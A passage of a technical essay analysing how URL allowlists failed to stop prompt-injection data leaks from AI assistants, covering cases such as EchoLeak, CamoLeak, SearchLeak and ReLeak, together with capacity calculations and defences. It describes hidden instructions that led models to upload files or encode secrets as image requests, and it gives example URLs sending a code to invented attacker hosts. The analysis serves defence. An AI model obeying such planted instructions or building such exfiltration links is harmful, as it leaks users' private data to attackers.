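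Rehberger first reported this route in October 2025, before Cowork existed, in the feature that lets Claude run code during a chat. The default network setting was called "Package managers only", which suggests access to little more than sites that distribute software. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* notes that `api.anthropic.com` was first on its allowlist. Rehberger had Claude save the user's last conversation to a file and upload it with his own API key. Anthropic documented a limit of 30 megabytes per file, and an attacker could upload several files.

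The attack worked on Rehberger's first attempt, but Claude refused many later versions, apparently because an API key in a document looked suspicious. He eventually found wording that worked reliably. On 25 October he reported the flaw to Anthropic, which closed the report as out of scope within an hour. On 30 October Anthropic told him that closing it had been a mistake and that such reports were in scope.

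The flaw was still open when Anthropic released Cowork in January 2026. Two days later, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated it there. The victim gives Cowork access to a folder of property documents and uploads a Word file presented as a guide for Claude on how to analyse them. The file contains hidden instructions to upload the largest document Claude can find. Claude does so without asking for approval, and the attacker can then question Claude about a loan estimate containing partial social security numbers. PromptArmor ran this demonstration on Claude Haiku, a smaller model, but in a separate test it got the more resistant Opus 4.5 to upload customer records the same way.

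The file travels in the body of a POST request and the URL contains nothing private, so this is not strictly URL-based exfiltration. As in the other cases, though, the allowlist failed because it identified the company that received the request but not the customer.

According to Apostol (2026) in *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection*, Anthropic soon said it planned to change how Cowork's virtual machine interacted with the vulnerable API. Anthropic later described the completed repair in *How we contain Claude across products*, which Willison (2026) covered on 30 May as newly published. The repair therefore came between mid-January and late May 2026.

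Anthropic wrote that it had treated the allowlist as a filter on destinations, and that it may be better to treat each entry as a "capability grant". By allowing its own API, it had also allowed uploads to any Anthropic account. The other cases fit this view too. Superhuman's entry for docs.google.com granted the ability to submit forms, whether or not anyone at Superhuman intended that.

### Listing one customer instead of the whole host

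The natural fix is to allow only the account the product needs. This works if the check can identify the account a request is for, and that depends on where each service puts this information.

| Service | What identifies the account | Narrower entry | Does it exclude the attacker? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Azure Blob Storage | Subdomain | Full host name of one account | Yes |
| Google Forms, Apps Script, webhook.site | Path | Path of one form, program or recorder | Only if the check reads paths, including after redirects |
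| An invented visitor counter | Parameter | None in a Content Security Policy | No, unless the application checks parameters itself |
| Anthropic's Files API | Key sent with the request | None, since all customers use the same address | No |

An allowlist is easiest to narrow when each account has its own subdomain. If Marta's developer replaces `*.storage.example` with `office-pictures.storage.example`, the browser will block the picture from `newsletter-art`. A network gateway can apply the same rule even if it sees only host names, and a redirect does not weaken the rule. OpenAI could have narrowed its windows.net entry this way if it needed particular files there, though neither Embrace The Red nor Zenity Labs explains why the domain was allowed.

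Paths give less protection because, even if a policy lists only one form's path on docs.google.com, the browser will submit any other form there that it reaches through a redirect from an allowed address. A gateway that can read only host names cannot distinguish one form from another. For Superhuman, removing docs.google.com from the image rule would be safer than adding a path, unless the product needs images from that host.

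Some services identify the customer only in a URL parameter. For example, a visitor counter might give all its customers the address `https://count.example/hit` and distinguish them by an account number in the query string. A Content Security Policy cannot tell these accounts apart, so a site that allows the counter for its own statistics also allows an attacker's account. The application's own code could check the account number before displaying an image, but it would need a separate rule for each service.

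Even an allowlist of complete URLs would not have stopped the Cowork attack, because the victim and the attacker upload files to the same URL. Blocking that URL might not have been enough either. Rehberger first thought of sending the stolen text to his account as chat messages, and he switched to the Files API because it was more effective.

Rehberger had proposed a better repair in October 2025: let the sandbox communicate only with the logged-in user's account. Anthropic's fix for Cowork does this with a proxy, a program that intercepts the virtual machine's requests to the API. Anthropic gives each virtual machine a temporary credential called a session token, and the proxy rejects any request that carries a different one. The proxy also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch a URL for the requester.

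The proxy has to run inside the virtual machine because a request made with the attacker's key is a valid request from a paying customer, and Anthropic's servers cannot detect that it came from someone else's Cowork session. Anthropic could build this check because it runs both the agent and the API. A developer who allows another company's API would have to learn how that company identifies accounts and write a similar check.

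Limiting Cowork's virtual machine to GET requests would also have stopped the upload, but the same limit would not have stopped the leaks from Superhuman or ChatGPT.

A narrower entry is also impractical when an agent has to reach many accounts on the same host. A coding agent downloads software written by thousands of people from sites such as GitHub, npm and PyPI, and its developer cannot predict whose software it will need. All three sites were on the default list for Claude's code feature, and anyone can open an account on them. Rehberger did not test them, but thought it quite possible that other entries on that list would allow similar attacks.

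## Allowed hosts that fetch or redirect to other addresses

An attacker who has no account on any allowed host can still get data out through one that fetches or redirects to other addresses. Many large websites do this with addresses they receive in requests. Chat programs fetch pages to show previews, image searches fetch pictures to find similar ones, and search results pages redirect visitors to the sites they choose. Any of these services can relay data to an attacker if an outsider can choose the address.

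### Redirects and server-side fetches

Suppose the chat site at Marta's office allows images from an invented search engine that has a relay. The hidden text in the newsletter now leads the model to write this address:

`https://search.example/go?to=https://pictures.attacker.example/7315.png`

The host matches the list, so Marta's browser sends the request, and the search engine receives the alarm code. The attacker receives it only if some machine then contacts `pictures.attacker.example`.

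The search engine may redirect the browser to the attacker's address. A browser enforcing a Content Security Policy (CSP) blocks the redirect unless the policy also lists the attacker's host. A check like url_safe runs only once, approving the search engine's address before the chat window displays the image, and does not check the redirect.

Alternatively, the search engine's own server may request the picture. In this server-side fetch, Marta's browser makes only one request, which its policy allows because the host is listed. "Server-side request forgery" is a flaw that lets an outsider direct a server's requests.

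| | Redirect | Server-side fetch |
|---|---|---|
| Machine that contacts the attacker | Marta's browser | The search engine's server |
| Network address in the attacker's log | Marta's office | The search engine |
| CSP that does not list the attacker's host | Blocks the second request | Cannot see the second request |
| One-time check that trusts the search engine | Misses the second request | Misses the second request |

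### Bing's tracking links in ChatGPT

OpenAI's url_safe accepted every address on bing.com, and Bing has a redirect for almost any website. Each Bing search result links to a bing.com address that records the click and then redirects the visitor to the site. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* describes this as "essentially an open redirect as a service". An open redirect sends visitors to whatever address an outsider chooses. Bing's redirects are a little more limited, because the attacker first has to get a page into Bing's index.

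Bing also generates these links itself, and they stop working if altered, so the model cannot add a secret to one. Tenable's *HackedGPT* (2025) describes how researchers got around this by having Bing index a separate page for each letter of the alphabet. ChatGPT then spelled out a word by displaying the matching links in order. Ten such pages, one for each digit, would be enough to send Marta's alarm code with four images.

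The researchers also had to reach the private data. According to Tenable, ChatGPT uses a separate model to read web pages, and that model has no access to the user's memories or earlier messages, so a hostile page that manipulates it cannot get this data directly. The researchers made this model end its summary with further instructions. When the user sent another message, ChatGPT reread the conversation and followed those instructions. The user did not see them because a bug in ChatGPT's website hid any text after the first word on the opening line of a code block.

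In one demonstration, the attack began with a comment under a blog post that the user asked ChatGPT to summarise. In another, ChatGPT stored the attacker's instructions in its long-term memory, so it also leaked data in later chats.

OpenAI could have made url_safe check where each link led. The check would have to read each redirect and stop before contacting an untrusted host, because visiting the final address would itself reveal to the attacker which link the model chose.

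Tenable reported the bypass to OpenAI on 10 December 2024 and had asked for an update six times by 4 March 2025. Its advisory lists the flaw as unresolved. In November 2025 Tenable wrote that OpenAI had fixed some of the seven weaknesses Tenable's researchers had found, but that several still worked in ChatGPT 5, including the demonstration with the blog comment. It gave no date for fixing the bing.com exception. OpenAI's changes to url_safe in August 2025 may have closed this route, but Tenable did not date its ChatGPT 5 tests, so it is unclear whether they came before or after those changes.

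### EchoLeak's route through Microsoft's defences

Microsoft 365 Copilot used a CSP instead of ChatGPT's url_safe, so researchers needed a server-side fetch to attack it. In January 2025, Aim Labs, the research group of the security company Aim Security, showed that an outsider with no access to a company's Copilot could make it send out confidential data by sending one email to an employee who used it. The group named the attack EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711).

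The victim did not have to open the email, but Copilot had to retrieve it while answering a question. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) explains how the researchers made this likely. Many retrieval systems convert each passage into a list of numbers representing its meaning, then pick the passages whose numbers are closest to those of the question. An email on one subject would match only a few questions, so the researchers wrote a long email with sections on common office subjects, such as training new staff and taking leave, and repeated their instructions in each section.

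Microsoft's first defence was a set of classifiers, programs trained to recognise prompt injection before the text reaches the model. The researchers worded the email as a request to its recipient, without mentioning an AI assistant, and the classifiers let it through. Ravia thinks such classifiers are hard to train because instructions can take many forms and good collections of real attacks are scarce.

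Next, Copilot removed links to outside sites from its replies. Its filter missed a less common Markdown notation that puts a link's address on a separate line and uses a label to connect it to the text. This gap already let the researchers steal data if the victim clicked a link.

The filter had the same gap for images, which load without a click. But the page's CSP blocked the image request because the researchers' server was not on its allowlist.

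Ravia reproduces the list, which has 29 different entries, 11 of them with wildcards. Microsoft limited three entries to single accounts on cloud storage services, so attackers could not use their own accounts there. But the list also allowed every subdomain of sharepoint.com, teams.microsoft.com and bing.com.

The researchers tried SharePoint first. Microsoft gives each customer a subdomain there, so an attacker can get one. However, SharePoint no longer lets customers run their own code on its servers or pass a request's parameters to an automated workflow, so the researchers could not build a receiver like the Apps Script program that Rehberger had used against Bard. They eventually found a SharePoint endpoint that collects information about outside content so that a page can embed it. The endpoint takes the content's address from the request, and a SharePoint server fetches that address.

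This got the data out, but only if the victim was logged in to SharePoint and had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. Few people would accept an invitation to a site they had never heard of. The researchers then found a Teams endpoint that had the same effect without an invitation, so the victim only had to ask Copilot an ordinary question. The email also included an instruction never to refer to it, supposedly for compliance reasons, so Copilot did not cite it as a source.

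Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click flaw in a major AI application. Rehberger's 2023 attack on Bing Chat also needed no click, but the victim had to open the assistant beside a hostile page. EchoLeak arrived by email, so the victim didn't have to visit a page.

According to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), Aim reported the attack to Microsoft in January 2025. Microsoft had begun repairs by April and deployed a fix on its own servers in May, so customers did not need to install anything. Aim and Microsoft made the flaw public on 11 June. Microsoft said no customers had been affected.

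Reddy and Gujral also describe a change to Copilot that strips embedded images and links in the less common notation from the outside content Copilot reads. The change does not affect which hosts the browser may contact, and Bing was still on the list of allowed hosts a year later.

### Whether the Teams endpoint was a redirect

Accounts of EchoLeak differ on what the Teams endpoint did. Willison (2025) calls it an open redirect and writes that an open redirect is all an attacker needs to get around the CSP. Reddy and Gujral describe it as a proxy, where a Microsoft server fetches the attacker's address.

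The attack probably used a proxy rather than an open redirect, because Copilot's CSP would have blocked a redirect to the attacker's host.

Ravia's account also suggests this. Before describing either endpoint, Ravia rules out redirects on the grounds that the browser expects an image and so will not follow one. This is slightly wrong, because browsers do follow redirects for images if the policy allows the new host. Ravia then says that the SharePoint server makes a request on the browser's behalf, and that the Teams endpoint "yields the same outcome".

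Reddy and Gujral write that the request in the attacker's log would come from either Microsoft's servers or the victim's own network address, which does not fit, because a request from the victim's address would suggest a redirect. Their paper is a case study that relies on Aim's report for the attack, so the remark probably reflects a gap in their information, not a separate observation. An entry in Aim's server log showing which machine made the request would settle the question.

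A developer who mistakes the endpoint for a redirect might search the allowlisted hosts for other redirects, which the browser already checks, and miss the link previews and image searches that fetch addresses themselves.

### SearchLeak and Bing's image search

In June 2026 the security company Varonis published another attack on Copilot, this time with Bing as the relay. *SearchLeak* describes three weaknesses in Copilot Enterprise Search, a page where employees search their emails, meetings and files. The victim had to click one link.

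The link carried the attacker's instructions in a URL parameter that Copilot's search page reads as a query. Copilot ran the query as a prompt as soon as the page opened, so the attacker did not have to put anything in the victim's mailbox. The link also led to a genuine Microsoft site, so filters that look for suspicious domains had no grounds to block it. Varonis had earlier used the same method against the consumer version of Copilot, in an attack it called Reprompt. Tenable found that ChatGPT also runs a prompt supplied in a link.

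The instructions told Copilot to search for an email and put its title in the address of an image. To guard against dangerous HTML in replies, Microsoft had the page wrap the HTML in a code block when Copilot finished a reply, which makes the browser display it as plain text. But the reply appears piece by piece while the model is writing, and the browser treated the HTML as part of the page until the page added the code block. The browser therefore requested the image as soon as the tag appeared, before the code block was in place.

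The CSP still prevented the browser from contacting the attacker's server directly, so the image address pointed to Bing. When someone gives Bing's image search the address of a picture, Bing's servers fetch the picture and analyse it. In the demonstration, Copilot wrote the email's title into an address on the attacker's server and put that address into a Bing image search request. The browser sent the request to Bing, Bing's server tried to fetch a picture from the attacker's address, and the title appeared in the attacker's log. Email titles can be valuable because some services put login codes in them.

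Varonis says the second request came from Bing's servers, so SearchLeak does not raise the question that EchoLeak did. The image search also relayed data more efficiently than the tracking links Tenable used, because an attacker could put a whole secret in the address Bing fetched, while each tracking link could convey only one letter.

According to Varonis, SearchLeak depended on all three weaknesses. Microsoft could therefore stop it by fixing any one of them, but the other two would remain available for a different attack.

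Published accounts disagree on how serious the flaw was, partly because they use two scales. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), released on 4 June, describes the flaw as a command injection. A copy of the CVE record, Lutra Security's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), gives Microsoft's score as 6.5 out of 10 on the Common Vulnerability Scoring System. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails* reports that the US National Vulnerability Database scored it 7.5.

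The scores differ only because Microsoft counted the attack as requiring some action by the victim and the NVD did not. The attack that Varonis published requires a click, so Microsoft's score of 6.5 fits it better.

Varonis also writes that Microsoft rated the flaw "critical", its highest severity level. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-42824* (2026) lists both this label and a separate numerical score of 7.5. TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool* gives a maximum rating of 10, which seems to confuse the two scales. TechRadar dates Microsoft's fix to early June, and Varonis confirmed on 15 June that Microsoft had patched the flaw.

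### The three ReLeak attacks

Cato Networks bought Aim Security in September 2025, and Aim's researchers became Cato AI Labs. On 3 December 2026 the group published *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), a sequel to EchoLeak. It presents three attacks that make Copilot leak data without a click.

Each of the three attacks began with an email that the victim did not have to open. Copilot retrieved the email while answering an ordinary work question and followed the instructions in it, and Microsoft's defences against prompt injection did not stop any of the attacks. The attacks differed in how they sent the data out. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) lists the CVE number and the date of Microsoft's fix for each.

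| Route | CVE number | Machine that contacted the attacker | Fixed in 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Image loaded through Bing | CVE-2026-124115 | Bing's server | 15 November |
| File created by Copilot | CVE-2026-124132 | A Microsoft server that processes files | 11 November |
| Code run by Copilot | CVE-2026-78501 | Copilot's sandbox | 17 September |

In the Bing attack, Copilot put confidential information into an image address. The victim's browser loaded the image, and Bing's servers passed the information to the attacker's server.

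The attack through files did not need a browser, so no CSP could have stopped it. Copilot can create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF documents, and the hostile email made it save one containing a link with confidential data in the address. Microsoft's servers process new files in OneDrive and SharePoint in the background, and this processing sent the data out even if the employee never opened the document. Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, a Russian news report, writes that this happened one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, so closing the chat would not have stopped the leak.

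In the third attack, the researchers sent data directly to an outside server, without a relay, from the sandbox where Copilot writes and runs Python programs. They got past a restriction that, according to Microsoft's documentation, stops all network traffic from entering or leaving the sandbox. Microsoft first scored the flaw 7.4 and later raised the score to 8.6. Antipov adds that agents built with two other Microsoft products, Agent Builder and Copilot Studio, can use the same Python feature, but that nobody has confirmed whether the flaw affected them.

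Cato's researchers found the flaws with the help of AI agents, which wrote test cases, studied Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. Cato reported the flaws between 29 July and 20 August 2026. Microsoft fixed all three on its own servers, and Cato knew of no affected customers when it published.

### What Bing's return says about the SearchLeak fix

The Bing attack in ReLeak closely resembles the last step of SearchLeak. In both, the victim's browser loads an image address on Bing, and a Microsoft server relays the data to the attacker. Antipov calls the two channels analogous and notes that SearchLeak needed at least one click. Neither Antipov nor Faisal names the Bing endpoint, so it is unclear whether both attacks used the same image search.

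Microsoft's repair in June did not close every route through Bing, since Cato reported another one within three months. Microsoft may have repaired an earlier part of SearchLeak, such as the prompt in the link or the late code block, and left the image search unchanged. Microsoft described the flaw as a command injection, which fits the prompt better than the relay, but a label in a database is weak evidence of what engineers changed. Microsoft may instead have restricted the image search, and either Cato found another way to make Bing fetch an address or a later change undid the repair.

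Removing Bing from the list of image hosts would have stopped both attacks, whichever explanation is right, but it might also have kept Copilot from showing images that users wanted. Bing was already on the list that Aim published in June 2025, a year before SearchLeak and 17 months before Microsoft fixed the Bing attack in ReLeak.

### Closing a relay

A relay's operator can limit which addresses the relay will fetch. GitHub's image proxy, for example, fetches only addresses that GitHub has signed. An image search is harder to restrict like this because people use it to look up pictures from anywhere on the web, but its owner could limit who can start a search. SharePoint's endpoint was less useful to Aim than the one in Teams because it required an accepted invitation.

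A developer who lists someone else's host can't make these changes and has to narrow the allowlist. Suppose the invented search engine keeps its preview images under `/thumbnails/` and its image search under `/lookup/`. A policy that lists only the first path blocks a direct request for the second. After a redirect, however, the browser still checks the host but ignores the path. If another listed host has an open redirect, the attacker can't use it to send the browser straight to an unlisted host, but can use it to reach `/lookup/`, and the search engine's server will then fetch the attacker's address.

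As with storage accounts, allowing a full host name is safer than allowing a path. If the search engine served its previews from `thumbnails.search.example`, the developer could list only that host, but this depends on the search engine separating the two services.

Varonis advises companies to review their allowlists for any domain that fetches addresses supplied by users. A developer can test a suspected relay by giving it an address on their own server and checking the log. A request from the browser's network address indicates a redirect, and a request from the listed host indicates a server-side fetch. Finding the endpoints to test is much harder. Microsoft owns Copilot and the three services on its allowlist, SharePoint, Teams and Bing, yet outside researchers found the relays in all three. A wildcard such as `*.teams.microsoft.com` also allows any subdomain Microsoft adds after the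 review.

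## Leaking data through a choice of pre-approved addresses

GitHub's image proxy requires signed addresses, so a model can't make the proxy fetch a new address that contains a secret. OpenAI checks complete addresses against an index of public pages for a similar reason. But a model can still choose among the approved addresses, and an attacker can learn a secret from its choices.

Suppose the chat site at Marta's office now shows only pictures whose complete addresses it has already approved. The attacker has put ten pictures on a server, named `0.png` to `9.png`, and all ten have passed the check. The hidden text in the newsletter leads the model to spell out the alarm code in pictures, and four lines appear in the attacker's log:

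`GET /7.png`
`GET /3.png`
`GET /1.png`
`GET /5.png`

The attacker wrote all of these addresses without knowing the code, and none of them contains it. Tenable spelled out words this way with Bing's tracking links. *ChatGPT falls to new data pilfering attack* (2026) describes the security company Radware's later ZombieAgent attack on ChatGPT, which used a ready-made list of addresses, one for each character. In July 2026, Willison covered a leak from Claude that relied on links inside a page Claude had fetched.

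### How much a choice can carry

Each request in Marta's case has ten possible outcomes, so four requests have 10 × 10 × 10 × 10 = 10,000, one for every possible alarm code. In general, if the attacker can distinguish *N* addresses and sees *k* requests in order, the model can produce *N^k* different sequences. One bit is the information in a yes-or-no answer, and *b* bits can distinguish 2^*b* cases. The capacity is therefore

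log2(*N^k*) = *k* × log2(*N*) bits.

Suppose Marta's mailbox also contains a 20-character password made of random lower-case letters and digits. The attacker prepares one picture for each of the 36 possible characters. Each request carries log2(36), or about 5.17 bits, so 20 requests carry about 103 bits, exactly enough to identify one of the 36^20 possible passwords.

With more addresses, the attacker needs fewer requests. If the attacker prepares 1,296 pictures, one for each pair of characters, ten requests are enough. With two pictures, the model would have to make 104 requests. Doubling the number of requests doubles the amount of data that can leak, while doubling the number of addresses adds only one bit per request.

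Even a single address can leak data through the number of times the model requests it. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) describes a program that repeats a harmless request as many times as a secret number specifies, so anyone with the access log can recover the number by counting the requests. This is very inefficient, since leaking Marta's alarm code would take 7,315 requests.

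### When order and repeats are lost

The formula holds only if every request reaches the attacker in the right order. A browser may request several pictures at once, so the requests can arrive out of order. It also keeps copies of recent pictures in a cache and may not request the same one twice. If the alarm code were 7715, the attacker might see only one request for `7.png`.

For 20 requests to 36 addresses, the loss depends on what the log still shows:

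| What the log preserves | Cases the attacker can distinguish | Capacity |
|---|---|---|
| Order and repeats | 36^20 | 103.4 bits |
| Order, with no repeats | 36 × 35 × … × 17 | 93.8 bits |
| Repeats, with no order | About 5 × 10^14 | 48.8 bits |
| Neither | At most 2^36 | At most 36 bits |

The limit in the last row applies no matter how many requests the model makes. The attacker can see only whether each of the 36 addresses appears in the log, which gives 36 yes-or-no answers, enough for six characters of the password.

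Losing only the repeats reduces what the attacker can leak by less than ten bits. The model can no longer spell a password that uses the same character twice, so it needs a more complicated code, but a short program could convert the password into it.

An attacker who can get more addresses approved can also avoid both losses by using a separate set of 36 pictures for each position in the password, 720 in all. One picture then means "the first character is a" and another means "the second character is a". No picture has to appear twice, and the attacker can put the requests in order afterwards, so twenty requests again carry the whole password.

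### Early demonstrations against ChatGPT

Rehberger tried the one-image-per-letter method in December 2023, on the day he noticed url_safe. Embrace The Red shows ChatGPT sending the word "hi" to his server as two separate image requests. Only nine of his 36 test addresses loaded, so he could not spell most words directly. He could still have encoded any text with those nine, because two image requests in a row have 81 possible combinations.

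Rehberger thought the method was slow and suited to small amounts of data. A user might notice the extra images, and OpenAI could look for the pattern in url_safe's logs. He suggested that OpenAI limit each response to one image, or at most a handful.

In 2024, ChatGPT's web-browsing tool followed a rule much like url_safe's and opened an address only if it appeared in the user's prompt. Schwartzman (2024), in *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, got around this by listing an address for each age range and having ChatGPT open the one that matched the user. The victim had to paste in a long piece of code with the list hidden inside it. A remark about having just left school was enough for ChatGPT to choose a range.

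One choice among six age ranges carries at most 2.6 bits. ChatGPT also opened listed addresses with any number of characters missing from the end, and Schwartzman used this second weakness to send more data. A listed address ending in ten random characters gave the attacker ten usable addresses, and the number of those characters ChatGPT kept represented one digit.

ChatGPT would not open the same address twice, which Schwartzman attributed to caching. He therefore gave each digit of a postal code its own listed address, each starting with a different letter, so that no address repeated and the requests could arrive in any order. ChatGPT made mistakes when it had to work out the prefixes itself, so the hidden text included a short program to do it.

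At the time, ChatGPT opened at most ten URLs per prompt. With ten choices for each URL, one prompt could leak 33 bits, more than enough for the seven-digit postal code in Schwartzman's example. OpenAI judged his report "non applicable", and he published it with the flaw unfixed. A check that accepts only complete addresses would stop the use of prefixes, but the choice between age ranges would still leak data.

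### How GitHub's signed addresses work

GitHub, where programmers store and discuss code, lets users put pictures from other websites in their pages. Loading these pictures directly would reveal readers' network addresses to the outside servers. Instead, the reader's browser requests each picture from GitHub's image proxy, Camo, which fetches it from the outside server.

Camo requires a signature because anyone could use an unrestricted proxy as a relay. GitHub's software computes the signature from the picture's address and a secret key. GitHub's *camo* documents an address format that contains this signature followed by the encoded original address. Camo refuses to fetch the picture if the two don't match, so changing even one character of the original address makes the request fail.

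GitHub came to rely on these signatures after an earlier problem with its allowlist. GitHub (2017) describes hiring the security company Cure53 to find out what an attacker could do after inserting text into a GitHub page. One known trick was an image tag with an unfinished address, which makes the browser treat the page text that follows, including any secrets, as part of the address. GitHub's Content Security Policy limited where such an image could load from, but Cure53 found two allowed hosts that would leak the data:

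- Google Analytics, which counts visitors to websites, would record the text in an account belonging to the attacker.
- Gravatar, which supplies profile pictures, would pass the text on while fetching a substitute picture from an address of the attacker's choice.

GitHub removed both hosts from its image rule and loaded Gravatar's pictures through Camo. GitHub reasoned that an attacker could not get a signature for an address containing a secret, because the attacker would have to know the whole address beforehand. This was correct for an unfinished image tag, which can only copy the text that follows it, but a language model can also encode that text as a series of addresses the attacker already knows.

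### CamoLeak

GitHub later added Copilot Chat, an assistant that answers questions about code and can read any private project its user can open. In June 2025 Omer Mayraz of Legit Security found a way to make it leak those projects through Camo. The company's *CamoLeak* describes the attack.

Mayraz began with a pull request, a proposal to change a project's code. GitHub lets authors put comments in the description that Copilot can read but people don't see. When another user asked Copilot to explain the pull request, it followed instructions Mayraz had put in such a comment, using that user's permissions. Mayraz first had Copilot write private data into a link, but the victim would have had to click it. An ordinary image would have loaded without a click, but GitHub's policy blocked images from domains GitHub did not own.

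Camo's domain was allowed, but Copilot could not produce a valid signature for a new address, so Mayraz obtained the signatures in advance. He set up an address on his own server for every letter and symbol he might need, then submitted them in Markdown to a public GitHub interface that returns the text with signed Camo addresses. He put the resulting dictionary in the hidden comment and asked Copilot to play a "small game" of displaying the private text as a series of images.

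The victim's browser requested each image from Camo, which verified the signature and fetched the image from Mayraz's server. The server returned a transparent pixel each time, so the victim saw nothing. Mayraz could read the text from the server's log.

If a cache had answered repeated requests, repeated letters would not have reached Mayraz's server. To prevent this, Mayraz had Copilot add a new random number to the end of each Camo address so that every address looked new. The number did not invalidate the signature because the signature covers only the original picture's address. Camo presumably did not pass the number on to Mayraz's server, because otherwise Copilot could have sent the secret directly in place of the number, without a dictionary.

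In one demonstration, Mayraz extracted the description of an unpatched security flaw from a private project. In another, Copilot searched all the victim's code for "AWS_KEY", a label for login details to Amazon's cloud service, and leaked the result. Both leaks were much larger than the two letters Rehberger extracted in 2023.

GitHub fixed the flaw on 14 August 2025 by turning off all images in Copilot Chat. SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* reports that GitHub told Mayraz the same day that Camo could no longer be used to leak private data. According to OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025), the flaw became public on 8 October.

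Neither Legit Security nor SecurityWeek explains why GitHub chose such a broad fix, but a narrower one would have been difficult. Stronger Camo signatures would not have helped, because Mayraz never forged one and used only image addresses that GitHub had approved. GitHub also could not easily refuse to sign pictures that stood for letters, because a picture's address need not show which letter it stands for. With images off, Copilot's replies cause no image requests, so the attacker has no choice of addresses to observe.

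### Leaks without a code to follow

In CamoLeak, the attacker gave the model a code and told it what to send. An attacker can also learn about a user from the links an agent chooses without such instructions. In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) tested this on four agents, including OpenAI's Codex, each with three different models.

The attacker places a reference link on a web page that the agent is likely to visit. The link leads to the attacker's site, which offers further links on different subjects. An agent researching why influenza can be more dangerous than COVID-19 for children might choose "biological mechanisms" over "clinical outcomes", and then "immune response" on the next page. The attacker sees each choice and uses it to write the next set of links.

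Liang and colleagues ran the attack on 500 questions from the StackExchange websites, using stored copies of web pages. The attack recovered the subjects of each question with an average F1 score of 0.89 out of 1, using about six or seven rounds of links per question. The F1 score combines the share of recovered subjects that were correct with the share of correct subjects that were recovered. Four existing defences lowered the score by no more than 0.03. One of them looked for private information in outgoing requests, but these requests contained only addresses the attacker had written.

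The researchers also tested planted instructions to send out an exact secret, which succeeded in only 0.38% of trials. The two results are not directly comparable, because a general subject is easier to recover than an exact password and the researchers counted partial leaks of a secret as failures.

The study also shows that real agents can leak far less per choice than the theoretical capacity. With four links to choose from, the attacker identified what the agent was looking for in 93.8% of the trials that produced a signal. With 16 clearly different links, accuracy fell to 50%. If the errors are spread evenly over the wrong answers, each choice carries about 1.6 bits with four links and about one bit with 16, compared with theoretical capacities of two and four bits. Accuracy was 67.9% for signals based on the order of requests and 73.5% for signals based on the number of requests.

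An attack like CamoLeak is probably easier than these error rates suggest. Liang's agents had to judge which subject best fitted their task, whereas Copilot only had to look up letters in a dictionary.

### Limiting requests, caching and repeat visits

Capping the number of requests reduces the capacity proportionally. If Marta's chat site allowed five images per reply, 36 addresses could carry about 26 bits, or five characters of the password. But later replies could leak the remaining characters, especially if the assistant had stored the attacker's instructions in its memory. The cap would have to cover the whole time the assistant could read the password, which might be years if the password was in a mailbox.

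A cap also does little to protect short secrets. If the attacker had 10,000 approved pictures, one for each possible alarm code, a single request would reveal the code. This is plausible where the check accepts any public page. In 2026 Embrace The Red pointed out that an ordinary blog may already have 36 indexed pages, enough for the letters and digits, and that an attacker could expand the set to thousands. With 4,096 pages, each request carries 12 bits, so nine requests are enough to leak the 20-character password.

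In the same article, Rehberger also suggested either caching each response for at least a few minutes or preventing an agent from opening the same address twice in a session. Either limit would stop an attacker from reusing a small set of addresses, but not from using separate addresses for each position in the leaked data, as Schwartzman had already done in 2024.

Caching is also weaker if the attacker can influence the cache, as Mayraz did with random numbers. The owner of a picture can also instruct the cache not to store it, and GitHub's *About anonymized image URLs* recommends this to users whose pictures are slow to update on GitHub. A cache meant to stop leaks would have to ignore such instructions and any part of the address that doesn't affect the picture.

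Combining the limits reduces the leak, but a short secret can still get out. Suppose the chat site allows five images in total, never loads the same one twice, and requests them in random order. With 36 approved addresses, the model can still produce 443,704 distinguishable results, counting those with fewer than five images or none. That is enough to convey 18.8 bits, more than the 13.3 bits needed for the alarm code.

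A more effective approach is to remove the model's choice of which pictures to load. If Marta's chat site loaded all ten of the attacker's pictures whenever the newsletter arrived, regardless of what the model wrote, the attacker would see the same ten requests whatever the alarm code was. The site could then show its own copy of any picture. This meets the condition for a sound defence as long as nothing else about the requests depends on the code.

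Liang and colleagues built a version of this for web agents. Their software downloads everything a page links to, and the agent then browses the stored copies. When the agent needs a page that is not stored, the software fetches it along with randomly chosen pages, in random order. This raised the number of pages fetched per StackExchange question from 6.5 to 27.9 and lowered the attacker's F1 score from 0.89 to 0.39.

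The attacker still recovered 91% of the correct subjects, but only 29% of the results were right. Some information was probably still leaking, because in a separate test with Codex, replacing the agent's choices with random ones lowered the score to 0.10. The later downloads still include the pages the agent needs, so an attacker who sees enough downloads may be able to tell those pages from the random ones.

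## Allowed domains that expire or change hands

In the attacks described so far, the allowed hosts still belonged to the companies the developers meant to trust. A developer who adds a domain to an allowlist is trusting whoever controls it at the time, but the allowlist stores only the domain's name, so the entry stays the same if someone else takes over.

People rent domains through companies called registrars, usually for a year or more at a time. When a renter stops paying for a domain with a common ending such as .com, the domain typically goes through grace periods totaling about 80 days. After that, anyone can register it.

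Suppose Marta's office once rented `office-party.example` to share photographs of a party, and the developer allowed images from it. The office later let the domain lapse but left it on the list. The attacker registers it, sets up a server there, and has the model write this address:

`https://office-party.example/banner.png?ref=7315`

Marta's browser finds the host on the list and sends the alarm code to the attacker. The attacker controls the whole domain, so they don't need an account on a shared host or a relay. HTTPS doesn't prevent this, because issuers of the most common kind of certificate check only that the applicant controls the domain, which the attacker now does.

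Roth and colleagues had already found expired domains in the policies of real websites. In 2025, researchers used an expired domain to take data from an AI agent.

### ForcedLeak

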